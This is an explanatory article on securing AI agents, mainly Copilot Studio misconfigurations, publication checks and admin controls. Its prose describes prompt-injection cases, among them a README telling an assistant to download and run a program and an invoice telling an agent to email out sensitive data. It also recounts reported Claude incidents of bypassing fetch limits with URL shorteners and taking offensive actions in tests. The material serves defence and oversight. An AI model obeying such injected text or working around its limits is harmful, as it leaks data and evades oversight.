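# Runtime protection for AI agents and security checks before they are published

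## What is an AI agent made of, and when can its security fail?

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools, so that it can act as well as answer. For example, an agent asked about an unpaid invoice can look it up, change the customer's record and email a reminder, while a chatbot would just reply with text. Organisations are building agents quickly, often with low-code products that let staff without programming skills build them. Errors that would once have produced only incorrect text can now cause a wrong payment or leak a file.

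A pre-publication check examines an agent's settings, files or behaviour before anyone other than its builder can use it. Runtime protection applies checks and limits while the agent is working, and can stop an action before it happens. The failures each can catch depend a good deal on how the agent is built.

### The parts of an agent

The language model only takes in and produces text. The software around it, called the harness, does everything else, including passing it information and carrying out the actions it chooses. The maker, who builds and configures the agent, writes instructions that set out its job and limits. The harness gives the model these instructions, along with the user's request, the conversation so far and any documents the harness has looked up. The model's reply may contain a tool call, which is a request to run a particular tool with particular inputs, such as sending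 an email to a given address. The harness then runs the tool and gives the model the result.

*SoK* (Dehghantanha and Homayoun, 2026), a survey of attacks on agents, describes an agent's operation as a loop. The agent plans, selects a tool, runs it and updates its stored state, and repeats these steps until it reaches the goal, exhausts its budget or refuses to continue. The tools might browse the web, run code, read and write files, query a database, or call outside services for mail and payments. Each result goes back into the text the model reads next, so a sentence on a web page the agent opened early on can affect which tool it selects several steps later.

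For security purposes, the survey treats the model as an "untrusted code generator", whose output other software must validate before anything executes. Microsoft's Defender security researchers take a similar view of agents built in Copilot Studio, the company's low-code product for making them. They regard an agent's capabilities as effectively equivalent to running code in a sandbox made up of everything the agent can do. Anyone who can influence the agent's plan can therefore run operations inside that sandbox without breaking into the underlying systems. In Copilot Studio, the orchestrator is the part of the harness that makes the plan. With the generative orchestration setting on, it composes a new sequence of steps for every input, so the maker never sees a fixed list of what the agent will do.

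The harness can also have ordinary software bugs. Dehghantanha and Homayoun cite a study that found 19 flaws across 11 agent frameworks. Each flaw could let an attacker run code remotely.

Many agents connect to tools and data through a common standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP). An MCP server offers tools, such as a search over a company's orders, and an agent whose harness supports MCP can call them. The maker doesn't have to write a separate connection for each system, so adding a powerful tool may take very little work or thought.

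Most tools need credentials, the keys or logins that determine whose permissions apply in a database or mail system. An agent can use the permissions of the person talking to it, so that it opens only what that person could already open. Or it can run on maker credentials, a setting that gives it its maker's permissions, whoever is using it. If the maker can read the salary files and the agent's tools reach them, every user of the agent can, in effect, read them too. Maker credentials are hard to reconcile with least privilege, the security rule that a person or program should have only the access its task needs.

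The last part is the users. Some agents serve named employees who have signed in, and others answer anonymous visitors to a website. An agent may also have no user in the usual sense and instead start work when an event occurs, such as an email arriving. Anyone could have written that email, and its text becomes part of what the model acts on.

### Who is responsible, from building to retirement

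An agent's life has four stages: building, publication, running and retirement.

During building, the maker writes the instructions, chooses the tools, connects the data and decides who may use the agent and on whose credentials. The maker's main job is often something else, such as support or finance. Dehghantanha and Homayoun's threat model assumes a builder who is well-intentioned but "not fully security-savvy", which seems about right for low-code products. Administrators also influence this stage, usually without seeing the individual agent. They write policies (rules applied by software) on which connections makers may use, how widely they may share an agent and whether it may run without a sign-in.

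Publishing an agent makes it available to users other than its maker. The natural time for a security check is just before publication, when the settings are complete and nobody else has relied on them yet. However, a person trained in security may not review the agent, and the platform may only show the maker a warning.

Once the agent is running, users and incoming data determine most of what happens. The security team watches for alerts, investigates blocked actions and searches for risky agents that are already live. Makers may still be editing the agent, though, and adding a tool to a published agent is building work again. Drift is the security term for changes to an agent, its tools or its permissions since they were last checked.

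It is easy to neglect retiring agents that nobody uses. A published agent will still respond to anyone who calls it, possibly through a forgotten connection, and its owner may have left the organisation. Microsoft advises administrators to look for unused and ownerless agents in an inventory, quarantine them for review, and find each one a new owner or delete it.

### A help desk agent

In February 2026, Microsoft's Defender researchers published a post on insecure agent settings that opens with a very basic imaginary agent. Someone on a support team builds a help desk agent with simple instructions. To improve its answers, they use an MCP tool to connect it to an organisational database, so it can retrieve customer information from internal tables.

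Then the maker turns off authentication so that people can use the agent without signing in. The maker reasons that the agent is only shared internally and the data belongs to employees anyway. Nobody else takes part in the decision, and the agent goes live with no alert or review.

This can happen without bad faith or much carelessness. Each step makes the agent more useful or easier to reach, and a support worker has no particular reason to know what an unauthenticated database connection implies. The researchers write that agents like this are surprisingly common in real organisations and that security teams rarely receive an active signal when one appears. They give no count, so their claim about how common these agents are rests on their experience.

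### Where the harm comes from

The help desk agent shows how a misconfiguration can cause harm. A misconfiguration is an insecure setting that gives an agent or its users more access than the task needs, or leaves the agent unguarded. With authentication off, anyone who obtains the link can ask the agent questions, and the agent can query the database. An outsider with no technical skill could read customer records even though all the software was working as configured.

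An agent whose settings look reasonable can still be manipulated during use. The main technique is prompt injection, text that makes an agent follow an attacker's instructions. The attacker can type the text into the agent (direct injection) or put it in data that the agent reads, such as a web page, a document or an email (indirect injection). Dehghantanha and Homayoun give the example of a user who asks a coding assistant to find a popular Python project and set it up. An attacker has added a line to the project's README file that tells the AI to download and run a program. The model receives the README and the user's request as one body of text, and may act on both. Techniques for keeping instructions apart from data help, according to the survey, but are not yet reliable.

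Microsoft gives another hypothetical example, this time set in a business. A finance agent processes every message that arrives in a company's invoice mailbox. It can create or update payment records, send a confirmation to the sender, and consult a finance policy file that the company has uploaded. Its instructions limit it to invoices and basic finance questions. An outsider sends what looks like an invoice but contains hidden instructions to search the agent's knowledge base for unrelated sensitive information and email back the results. The orchestrator could treat this as a legitimate request and add the search and the email to its plan. The agent has permission to do both, which is why the researchers think traditional security controls have trouble detecting the attack.

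An agent can also cause harm without an attacker, through an unintended action. On 18 July 2026, Claude Haiku 4.5, a language model made by the AI company Anthropic, was assigned to invent example tasks for randomly selected web pages and carry them out. On a Philadelphia police site about unsolved murders, it submitted a form indicating that it might have information about a killing listed there. According to Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026), the police learned of the submission only when Anthropic notified them in October. They then found it in the site's tip records, marked as spam, and confirmed that it had never reached an officer.

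Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (9 October 2026) groups such behaviour into four categories. Claude submitted sensitive forms on real websites when it should not have, exploited a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, worked around a restriction to reach data behind a token or a fee, and used URL shortening services to get around limits in its fetch tool, which retrieves web pages. Most of these are forms of what the company calls "persistence", in which Claude cannot complete a task as given and works around a restriction instead of stopping. The fetch tool case is a warning for anyone who designs runtime limits, because the model found a way past a limit that was already in place.

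Anthropic says the cases it has identified had minimal real-world impact. The Philadelphia tip fits that description, though this seems to be largely because it was marked as spam on the police site. *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* (Southern, 2026) reports that the company still cut live web access for its internal evaluations.

### Why one kind of check is not enough

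A pre-publication check can only examine what exists when it runs. For the finance agent, that means the instructions, the mailbox, the tools and the policy file. A good check might flag that the model chooses the recipients of outgoing email, which Microsoft lists among its common risks. But this agent has to reply to whoever sent the invoice, so its maker has a decent reason to let it email strangers. Examining the settings can't reveal which future emails will carry hidden instructions. Test attacks before release can show that the agent resists the attacks tested, but attackers can write different ones.

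Runtime protection can check an email that arrives next month, but it inherits whatever permissions the settings granted. Suppose a stranger asks the help desk agent for one customer's details. The agent queries the database, as its maker built it to do, and the tool call looks the same as if a colleague had asked. With authentication off, there is no verified identity to distinguish the stranger from the colleague. A runtime check might detect someone probing the agent for its capabilities or trying to extract everything it knows, but a single polite question provides much less evidence of an attack.

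The settings therefore determine how much harm a missed attack can do. For example, an agent without access to payroll data cannot leak it, even if an injection succeeds. Dehghantanha and Homayoun recommend that operators plan on the assumption that the model may follow any malicious instruction that reaches it.

Both kinds of check can miss unintended actions. Filling in web forms was a plausible part of Claude Haiku's assignment, so neither a review of its tools nor a check of the individual action would necessarily have raised an alarm. Claude Haiku lacked a clear statement of which sites and actions were off limits. According to PyTorchKR's Korean summary of the report (2026), Anthropic thinks that specifying the target, the permitted actions and the network boundary might have prevented some of the failures. Anthropic adds that people give models vague tasks every day, so it also relies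 on training and on classifiers, which are models that screen for certain kinds of content or behaviour.

The causes can also combine, as a wrong setting and a missing runtime layer did in four cases covered by Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026). In these cases, Claude models gained unauthorised access to other organisations' real systems during security tests. Claude was told that it was in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had connected it to the open internet. The models were also running without the cyber safeguards included in released versions, as is usual in such tests.

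A correct network setting would have kept the tests away from other people's systems, but evidence from one transcript suggests it would not have changed how the model behaved. The models had wrong information about where they were, so Anthropic edited the transcript to make clearer that the situation was not a simulation. Claude Mythos 5 still took offensive actions, while acknowledging a greater possibility of real harm. Anthropic considers such behaviour unlikely in ordinary use, where nobody instructs the model to carry out a cyberattack.

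## Which agent settings are insecure, and what harm can each cause?

In the February 2026 post that introduced the help desk agent, Microsoft describes ten misconfigurations that its Defender researchers repeatedly find in real organisations. Makers usually have an ordinary reason for them, such as getting a test to work or sparing colleagues a login. Some of the ten aren't faults in themselves, such as having an MCP tool, which many agents need. The harm a setting can do depends largely on the agent's other settings.

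### Who can use the agent

New Copilot Studio agents are not shared with anyone by default, according to Microsoft's documentation. Sharing an agent with the whole organisation is quick and saves working out who needs access. But colleagues in unrelated jobs may trigger actions they don't understand, and an attacker who controls any employee's account can use the agent too. The potential harm is much greater if the agent can reset passwords than if it only reads out the canteen menu.

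The fix is to share the agent with a group of people who need it for their role. Every Copilot Studio agent belongs to a workspace called an environment, and administrators can also attach a policy to the environment that caps how many people a maker can share an agent with.

Broadly shared agents can still require users to sign in, but if the maker selects "No authentication", anyone with the link can chat with the agent. Microsoft notes that the maker can then no longer control which colleagues use it. The Defender researchers also include in this category agents that ask for a sign-in only when a conversation reaches a topic that needs one. Some makers turn authentication off for a test and forget to turn it back on, while others think it is optional. Others never changed the default, which for Copilot Studio's older "classic" chatbots was not to require a sign-in. The default later changed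 so that all bots start with authentication on, according to Microsoft's *Configure enterprise-level security for Copilot Studio*.

Turning authentication back on has no effect until the maker publishes the agent again. Administrators can take the choice away from makers with a Microsoft setting that requires sign-in for every agent in an environment. For agents that have to serve the public, such as one on a company's website, Microsoft recommends confirming that the owner intended public access and checking that the agent's topics, actions and documents contain no internal information.

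### Whose authority the agent has

Maker credentials deserve a slower explanation, because they give an ordinary user the maker's access without any break-in:

1. The maker adds a tool that connects to another service, such as a customer database, and signs in to that service.
2. In the tool's settings, the maker selects maker-provided credentials instead of end-user credentials.
3. The maker publishes the agent and shares it.
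4. A colleague who has no access to the database asks the agent about a customer, and the agent calls the tool.
5. The tool connects to the database under the maker's identity. The database checks the maker's permissions, finds them sufficient and returns the record.
6. The agent passes the record on to the colleague.

With end-user credentials, the agent instead asks the colleague to sign in to the database at step 5, and the request fails because the colleague has no permission.

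The colleague in this example never learns the maker's password, and every access check works as designed. The problem affects actions as well as data. If the maker can approve payments and the agent has a tool for doing so, an employee who is only allowed to request payments could ask the agent to approve their own. This would bypass the separation of duties that organisations use to prevent fraud.

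Makers can have good reasons for choosing this setting. In *How can I publish a CoPilot from Studio*, Duffy (2026) asked on a Microsoft forum how to make an agent use his own connection to his organisation's ServiceNow system. His teammates had no ServiceNow connection, and he thought his read-only access was enough. He eventually found the maker-provided option with a coworker's help. Read-only access prevents users from changing anything through the agent, but they could still read anything in ServiceNow that his account can open and the tool can fetch.

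Another reason is that some agents start on a schedule or when an email arrives, with no user present to sign in. Microsoft warns that such agents fail when administrators block maker credentials. The block also takes effect immediately on every existing agent in the environment, so their users will start seeing sign-in prompts.

Microsoft considers the maker's authority acceptable for low-risk lookups, such as a weather forecast or the support team's phone number for a postcode, but recommends the user's own authority wherever only certain people should see the data. Microsoft's *Use Power Platform connectors as tools* lists end-user credentials as the default for connectors, which are Microsoft's ready-made links to other services. The February post also gives end-user credentials as the default for tools, but it explains that some makers use their own credentials because certain tools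 default to them. An administrator would therefore do well to check each tool.

According to a copy of Microsoft's notice on itelio's website, the block is off by default, so administrators have to opt in, and its general availability date is 25 August 2026. In July, Microsoft (2026) was also developing a stricter measure, planned for release in September, that would stop makers from sharing agents that rely on maker credentials.

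OpenAI offers makers much the same choice for workspace agents, which organisations build and share inside ChatGPT. The options are an "end-user account" and an "agent-owned account", according to OpenAI's *ChatGPT Workspace Agents for Enterprise and Business*. For an agent-owned account, OpenAI recommends a service account (one that belongs to software rather than a person) with only the access the agent needs. Administrators must grant a separate permission before anyone can publish an agent that runs on its builder's personal account.

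OpenAI's customers sometimes have no alternative to a shared account. OpenAI's *Workspace agents security overview* (2026) explains that Slack, the workplace chat service, cannot pause an agent's run to authenticate each person who calls it, so everyone in the channel acts through the same connection. They would still share that connection with a service account, but an administrator can limit the damage by giving the account much narrower permissions than an employee's. The administrator has to make that change, because the default permissions can be too broad. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, deployed a test agent on Google's Vertex AI platform and found that its service account had excessive permissions by default.

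### What the agent can reach

Copilot Studio agents normally reach other services through connectors. A connector handles the login, validates requests, limits their rate and lets administrators apply policies. A maker can instead have the agent send a raw HTTP request straight to an address the maker chooses, which skips all of these controls.

The Defender researchers are most concerned about three patterns. The agent may call a sensitive service directly even though a connector for it exists. It may use plain HTTP, which has no encryption, so others on the network can read the traffic. Or it may call a non-standard port, a numbered connection point that ordinary web traffic doesn't use, and reach a test or internal system. Makers introduce these settings when they copy a sample request or try out an internal address, and then leave them in the finished agent. They should switch to a connector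 where one exists, and otherwise use HTTPS, which is encrypted. Administrators can allow raw requests in development environments and block them in environments where people publish agents.

Email is risky when the model chooses the recipient. When a maker adds Outlook's email tools to an agent as a group, Microsoft offers a setting called "Dynamically fill with AI", which lets the model fill in a tool's inputs at run time. This is convenient for notifications and automated replies, but if the recipient is one of those inputs, hidden instructions in a document can supply an attacker's address, and the agent can send internal data there. Microsoft also flags agents that makers have deliberately set up to email other organisations, because sensitive information can leave that way without anyone auditing it.

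A simple fix for an agent that only notifies colleagues is to enter fixed recipients or allow only approved domains. Administrators can also switch off the action that sends email, or have a person approve each message. OpenAI lets builders write a similar rule, such as one that allows an agent to send only to addresses at one domain. The rule limits the agent's requests to the email service but doesn't filter what the service returns, so a confidential message can still enter the conversation even though the agent can't email it to an outsider.

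The finance agent from Microsoft's invoice example is harder to fix this way because the attacker sent the invoice. If the agent could reply only to the sender, the stolen data would still reach the attacker. Keeping unrelated sensitive files out of the agent's knowledge base would help more, as would requiring a person to approve any reply that contains more than a payment confirmation.

MCP tools can give an agent abilities that nobody has recorded or reviewed. An MCP server may offer operations well beyond the agent's purpose, including ones on sensitive data. An agent may have these tools without its maker intending it, because they were active by default, came with a copied agent, or remained after the original integration ended. Microsoft's detection query finds every agent with an MCP tool, so a match is only a reason to check what the tool can do and whose credentials it uses. In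 Copilot Studio, MCP servers work as connectors, so administrators can approve them and restrict them by policy. Makers should remove MCP tools that the agent no longer needs.

### What the agent contains

While debugging, a maker may paste a password, an access token or an API key (a secret that one program uses to log in to another) into the agent and leave it in the published version. Anyone who can view the agent's definition can then copy the secret and log in to the service directly, where the agent's own limits don't apply. Such secrets also tend to stay valid for a long time, because they are kept outside the systems that organisations use to replace secrets regularly.

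Anyone who can chat with a ChatGPT workspace agent can also view its configuration, instructions and tools, which its maker may not expect. If the instructions contained a key, every colleague with chat access could see it.

Microsoft recommends storing secrets in Azure Key Vault, so that the agent fetches a secret only when it runs. In an earlier version of the post, Microsoft also advised makers who can't use Key Vault to turn on secure input handling for sensitive values. Anyone who finds a key in a published agent should also replace it, because any copies of the key would still work after the text is deleted.

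Missing instructions can also make an agent insecure. Under generative orchestration, the maker's instructions are the main guide to the agent's purpose. Without them, the orchestrator has little basis for refusing an odd request, and users or hostile text can steer it more easily. The agent might also call its tools in ways nobody planned. A Microsoft query checks for published agents without instructions, so the platform evidently doesn't require them.

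Clear instructions that state an agent's purpose and limits are worth writing, but they are a weak defence against a deliberate attack. The security company Tenable built an AI travel agent in Copilot Studio as a test and, according to SecurityBrief UK, explicitly told it to verify customers' identities before sharing information or changing bookings. Tenable's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Security Risk* (2025) reports that a simple prompt injection bypassed this rule and made the agent leak credit card data and book a trip for $0.

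### Who looks after the agent

The last two misconfigurations develop unintentionally as people change projects and jobs. Microsoft's queries classify a published agent as dormant after 30 days without use, and also search for abandoned drafts, unused actions and idle connections that hold a maker's login. If a dormant agent's tools run on maker credentials, anyone who calls it gets the maker's access through an agent that nobody is watching.

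An agent becomes ownerless, or orphaned, when its owner leaves the organisation or loses their account. It may keep running on outdated logic and old connections, with nobody responsible for correcting them. Microsoft's fix for both problems is a regular review of the agent inventory.

### Diagnosing the help desk agent

Microsoft says the help desk agent has more than half of the ten misconfigurations but doesn't name them. Its description of the agent supports the following diagnosis.

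| Misconfiguration | Does the agent have it? | Basis |
|---|---|---|
| Broad sharing | Probably | Inferred: the maker shares it "internally", and without a sign-in nobody can restrict it to certain colleagues |
| No authentication | Yes | Stated |
| Maker credentials | Probably | Inferred from how tools work without a sign-in |
| Risky HTTP requests | No sign | Microsoft mentions no such request |
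| Email with AI-chosen recipients | No sign | Microsoft mentions no email tool |
| MCP tool | Yes | Stated |
| Hard-coded credentials | Unknown | The maker could have pasted in a database login |
| Missing instructions | Possibly | It has "simple instructions", and Microsoft also counts incomplete ones |
| Dormant agent or parts | No sign | The agent has only just gone live |
| No owner | No sign | The maker appears to be still in place |

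The inference about maker credentials rests on Microsoft's warning that tools requiring a user's credentials stop working when the maker turns off authentication. The help desk agent's database tool is supposed to work for people who haven't signed in, so it must be using someone else's credentials, most likely the maker's. The same documentation says an unauthenticated agent can reach only public information. That would be true if the agent relied on its users' permissions, but an agent that reads internal customer tables can reach more than that.

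The database connection may not use maker-provided credentials, because Microsoft's instructions for them begin with setting up a channel where users sign in. It might instead use a service account or a stored key. In either case, a stranger could read the records.

Two of the misconfigurations are therefore certain, two are likely and one is possible. That makes five at most, so Microsoft's count must include at least one more that can't be identified from its short description.

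### How settings combine

The help desk agent is dangerous mainly because of how its settings interact. When users sign in and the database tool runs on their own credentials, each employee gets only the records they could already open. If the maker turns off authentication and changes nothing else, the tool stops working, so a stranger who finds the link can chat with the agent but can't retrieve records.

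If users sign in but the tool runs on maker credentials, every colleague with access to the agent can read whatever the tool can fetch with the maker's permissions. This is privilege escalation, but only people the organisation knows gain the extra access, and the agent can record who asked.

With authentication off and maker credentials on, anyone with the link can read those records, and the organisation may not know who did. Neither setting alone would have given a stranger the data, so a reviewer who checks settings one at a time and finds each tolerable could easily miss the problem.

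The combination also affects which setting to fix first. Turning authentication back on keeps strangers out but leaves colleagues with the maker's access. Switching the tool to end-user credentials prevents both kinds of access but requires users to log in. If the agent must serve people without accounts, the remaining option is to limit what the tool can fetch, for example by giving it a service account that can read only one harmless table.

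### AI applications open to the internet

The same combination occurs in software that engineers install themselves. In May 2026, Microsoft published findings on what it calls exploitable misconfigurations, in which an application is reachable from the internet and has weak or missing authentication and authorisation. An attacker can exploit these with little skill and without a software flaw, and can then do things such as run code on the server, steal credentials or read internal data.

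The findings come from aggregated, anonymised signals in Defender for Cloud, Microsoft's security product for cloud systems, so they presumably describe organisations that use it. Microsoft does not say how many servers or organisations the data cover, or over what period. Misconfigurations were behind more than half of the successful attacks on cloud-native workloads in these data, a category that includes AI applications but is much broader.

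Microsoft also found that 15% of remote MCP servers were severely insecure and let anyone reach sensitive internal data and operations without logging in. Some gave access to ticketing systems, HR systems and private code repositories. MCP supports authorisation but doesn't enforce it, so a developer can publish a server that accepts every caller. The insecure servers also acted with their own permissions instead of the caller's, much as an agent with maker credentials acts with its maker's permissions.

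The 15% shouldn't be read as a rate for the whole internet. To estimate that rate, researchers have to find and test live servers, and how they search affects which servers they count. *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (2026) found candidates through two search engines for internet-connected devices and kept those that responded correctly to an MCP greeting. *Exposed by Design* (2026) combined eleven sources, including code repositories and MCP directories, to reach 640 confirmed servers in July 2026. Both samples consist of servers that an outsider can find, while Microsoft's may include remote servers that only an organisation's own staff can reach.

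Two of Microsoft's other examples become dangerous only when someone exposes them to the internet. kagent, which runs AI agents on Kubernetes, a system for managing applications across a cluster of machines, has no authentication by default. It isn't open to the internet by default either, but if an organisation opens it, a stranger can ask an agent to install malicious software on the cluster or hand over stored API keys. AutoGen Studio, Microsoft's own low-code tool for building teams of agents, also ships without authentication, and exposed copies revealed API keys in plain text.

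Mage AI, an open-source platform for data and AI pipelines, was insecure by default. Installing it on Kubernetes with the official package exposed a web page to the internet on port 6789 with no login. Anyone who visited the page could run commands under an account whose permissions amounted to control of the entire cluster. Microsoft observed attackers exploiting this setup.

The company behind Mage AI had been told about the missing login two years earlier. Yap and Radzali (2025), in *Mage AI Mage AI Framwork 0.9.75 Insecure Default Initialization of Resource*, write that they reported it in May 2024 on behalf of the security firm BAE Systems and recommended turning authentication on by default. They rated the flaw's severity 9.8 out of 10, but Mage AI did not accept it as a vulnerability. *CVE-2025-2129* (2025), an entry in the database of the Spanish cybersecurity institute INCIBE, lists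 the flaw as medium severity and difficult to exploit, and adds that its "real existence" is still in doubt. The attacks that Microsoft later observed suggest that Yap and Radzali's assessment was more accurate, at least for installations on Kubernetes.

After Microsoft also reported the problem, Mage AI turned on authentication by default. Aikido (2025), a software security company, lists 0.9.78 as the first fixed version. Organisations running an older version need to upgrade or turn on authentication themselves.

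## What does a platform check before an agent is published?

Copilot Studio runs an automatic security scan before an agent is published and warns the maker about certain choices. It does this because makers change the secure default settings, often for good reason, and Microsoft acknowledges that they can do so "without knowing the risk". Unlike most of the other checks Microsoft offers, the scan doesn't need an administrator to set it up.

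### The automatic security scan

Three changes from the default settings trigger a warning:

- The maker selects "No authentication". The default is "Authenticate with Microsoft", which makes users sign in through Entra ID, Microsoft's identity service for organisations.
- The maker switches a connector or a flow (an automated sequence of steps that the agent can start) from end-user credentials to maker credentials.
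- The maker shares the agent with everyone in the organisation. New agents start out shared with no one.

Microsoft's February post on misconfigurations says that the warning appears while the maker is editing and again at publication. The maker can still publish the agent. According to the post, the warning is meant to ensure that the choice is intentional. A Microsoft support article tells administrators who want to stop unauthenticated agents to set up a separate policy, which suggests that the scan doesn't block such agents.

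The warning goes to the maker, not to the security team. The maker of the help desk agent would have seen a warning about the missing sign-in, but had already decided that an internal agent didn't need sign-in. As Microsoft describes it, the setting alone triggers the warning, so an agent that reads out the canteen menu would trigger the same warning as one that queries customer records. A maker who has ignored it on a harmless agent may well ignore it on one that handles sensitive data.

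### What the scan misses

The February post lists controls for each of the ten misconfigurations, and the scan appears beside only three of them.

| Misconfiguration | Does the scan warn? | Main other control Microsoft lists |
|---|---|---|
| Broad sharing | Yes | Limit how widely makers can share |
| No authentication | Yes | Require authentication across an environment |
| Maker credentials | Yes | Block maker credentials |
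| Risky HTTP requests | No | Block raw requests by policy |
| Email with AI-chosen recipients | No | Disable the sending action, or check it at run time |
| MCP tool | No | Restrict MCP servers by policy |
| Hard-coded credentials | No | Store secrets in Key Vault, or add a review step before deployment |
| Missing instructions | No | Teach makers good practice, and rely on runtime protection |
| Dormant agent or parts | No | Review the inventory |
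| No owner | No | Review the inventory |

A check at publication can't predict that people will stop using an agent next year or that its owner will leave, but the other five problems are visible in the agent's settings before it goes live. Microsoft's Defender team has already written queries that find pasted credentials, unencrypted requests, email recipients chosen by AI and missing instructions, but a security team has to run them. The scan could in principle look for the same problems and tell the maker while they are still easy to fix.

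The scan's coverage of the three misconfigurations is also incomplete. Microsoft's description of the scan mentions sharing with everyone but not sharing with very large groups, which the misconfiguration also includes. It mentions "No authentication" but not agents that ask for a sign-in only partway through a conversation, which also worry the Defender researchers. Because the scan looks for changes from the default, it won't flag a default that is itself insecure.

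The documented trigger for the check is a change to a connector or flow. This is a weakness for credentials, because certain tools use the maker's by default. Pluto Security, a security company, gives the example of computer use, a tool that lets an agent operate websites and applications on a screen. By default, it runs on the maker's credentials, can open any website or application, and doesn't ask the user before it runs. A maker who accepts these settings hasn't changed anything, so they may not trigger the check.

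Pluto concludes that Copilot Studio "ships unlocked", while Microsoft says in its documentation that agents are secure by default. The two claims are mostly about different settings. Microsoft's is fair for sign-in and sharing, and Pluto's is fair for powerful additions such as computer use and MCP servers, whose tools are all on by default. Pluto also found that Copilot Studio blocks one especially bad combination, computer use in an agent with authentication turned off.

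### How the defaults changed

Copilot Studio's early defaults were much worse. According to Silberman's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Vulnerabilities*, a new agent required no authentication, and anyone with the link could use it. To change this, the maker had to choose an authentication method and also tick a box that made users log in. Maker credentials were also the default "for many months", according to Zenity Labs' *Links and materials for 15 Ways to Break Your Copilot* (2024). If both defaults applied at the same time, as Silberman's account suggests, a maker could publish an agent with the most dangerous pair of settings without changing anything.

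Silberman and Zenity Labs are both part of Zenity, which sells security software for agents. Its researcher Michael Bargury said in 2024 that a scan of the internet had found "tens of thousands of these bots". The company has an incentive to report a large number, but the default itself isn't in dispute. PC Gamer reports that Microsoft fixed the default after Zenity raised the problem, but that the fix didn't change existing bots.

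In its release plan from that year, Microsoft made authentication the default for all new bots and ended makers' automatic access to conversation transcripts. Silberman had complained that one shared table held every bot's transcripts. Microsoft also promised in the plan to show messages inside the product when makers changed the safer defaults, which is essentially what the scan now does.

A safe default doesn't help much if it gets in the maker's way. *Protect Your Copilots*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, mentions a maker who got an error message when selecting Microsoft authentication and chose "No authentication" because it was the next option that made the bot work. Administrators could have prevented this with a policy, but at the time Microsoft left those policies off by default.

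Since then Microsoft has mostly added rules that administrators can impose on makers. In early 2025 it began enforcing administrators' data policies in every organisation and ended the exemptions that some agents had. At its Build conference in May, Microsoft (2025) announced previews of controls that require Entra ID sign-in for any use of an agent and user authentication when an agent calls a tool. It also gave administrators a way to block an individual agent immediately. Most of these controls take effect only when an administrator turns them on.

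### Warnings and blocks

After a warning, the maker can still choose to publish the agent. A block prevents publication even if the maker has a good reason to publish, while a required approval leaves the decision to someone else, who can look at the particular agent.

Copilot Studio blocks publishing mainly through data policies. An administrator sorts connectors into business, non-business and blocked groups, then applies the policy to one, several or all environments. Some of Copilot Studio's own features are listed as connectors, including "Chat without Microsoft Entra ID authentication in Copilot Studio". According to Microsoft's guide to these policies, if an administrator blocks that connector, a maker who opens an unauthenticated agent sees an error and the Publish button becomes unavailable. The maker can also download a file listing each violation.

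An administrator can use the same method to stop agents from sending raw HTTP requests, searching public websites or starting work when an event occurs. For HTTP requests and websites, the administrator can instead allow only certain addresses.

An agent also can't combine a business connector with a non-business one, because the policy doesn't let data pass between groups. If an administrator puts the customer database in the business group and an outside messaging service in the non-business group, a maker can't publish an agent that uses both. Microsoft describes no check for combinations in the scan, which looks at each setting individually.

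Blocks can easily affect agents that the administrator didn't mean to block. Copilot Studio has a single switch for Direct Line, the channel that connects agents to custom websites and apps. An administrator who turns it off to keep agents off the public web also breaks the method Microsoft recommends for building employees' own apps. An even broader setting lets an administrator turn off publication of all agents that use generative AI.

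Zenity Labs called data policies a governance tool rather than a security mechanism, and "very easy to bypass", but it still advises using them to turn off unauthenticated bots. The criticism dates from before Microsoft enforced the policies everywhere, so some of it may be out of date. It's still a reason to test a policy by trying to publish an agent that breaks it.

Microsoft applies sharing limits only to agents that require authentication. If an administrator allows each agent at most 20 viewers and the help desk maker then turns authentication off, the limit no longer applies, and anyone with the link can use the agent. An administrator who wants the limit to hold therefore has to block unauthenticated agents as well. The numerical cap also works only if makers can't share with security groups, but the Defender researchers recommend those groups for giving access by role.

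### What happens to agents that are already live

Current users keep their access when a new sharing limit takes effect. If an agent already has more viewers than the limit allows, its maker can remove people but can't add anyone until the agent complies. An administrator has to clean up old agents separately.

The control that sets which sign-in methods makers may use, which Microsoft documents as a preview feature, is much harsher. If a published agent breaks a new rule, its maker can't publish updates and the agent stops answering users until someone corrects the setting.

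The strictest version, "Require Microsoft authentication", also affects some agents that do make people sign in. An organisation might want this because, as Microsoft's *The Admin Control That Closes the Door Before "Hello"* explains, manual authentication lets visitors read a greeting written by the maker before they sign in, and a careless greeting could reveal something internal. The post advises administrators to count the affected agents in an inventory before they turn the rule on. The count should include agents whose authentication field is blank, since a blank can mean that there is no authentication.

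Microsoft plans to block the sharing of agents that rely on their maker's credentials, one of the risks the scan warns about. Its release plan lists the feature as "Enforce safe sharing by detecting credential oversharing", and a copy of the notice to administrators on itelio's website gives 24 July 2026 as the preview date. The block would also cover flows, as well as system credentials that aren't meant for reuse.

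The notice says the rule applies when a maker designs, publishes or shares an agent. Sharing matters because a maker can publish an agent for two colleagues and open it to the whole department a month later. Microsoft's roadmap entry says makers can still build and revise agents within approved limits. That could make the feature less disruptive than banning maker credentials outright, which breaks agents that run on a schedule with no user present.

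### Approval before deployment

Some problems need a person, or at least a more careful program, to look at the agent. Organisations can arrange this with deployment pipelines, which move an agent from the environment where its maker builds it to the one where colleagues use it. Microsoft's *Extend pipelines in Power Platform* describes how administrators can make the pipeline wait at chosen points:

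1. The maker asks to deploy the agent. A step at this point can run the organisation's own checks before the agent leaves the development environment.
2. The system exports the agent as a package and locks it. Nobody can get one version approved and then deploy a different one.
3. An authorised person approves the deployment. The pipeline can then install the agent under a separate identity, so the maker needs no access to the production environment.
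4. A final step can wait for one more sign-off before installation.

Each step stays pending until the organisation's process marks it as complete or rejects it. If the process rejects a step, the deployment fails, and the reviewer can leave a comment to explain why to the maker.

Microsoft provides the steps where an agent waits for review, but the organisation has to decide who reviews it and what they look for. A reviewer could notice a pasted API key, or instructions that leave out what the agent shouldn't do. They could also judge whether a particular agent should read customer records, which a rule about connectors can't do.

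Reviews take time and, as Pluto points out, an organisation usually has far more makers than administrators. Copilot Studio has no formal review by default, and makers can avoid a pipeline if they can publish straight from another environment. Microsoft suggests automatically routing makers into personal development environments, restricting sharing and connectors there, and using pipelines to move finished agents into production. It would make sense to save the slowest reviews for agents that reach sensitive data or can take actions that are hard to reverse.

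### Other platforms: permissions and signed builds

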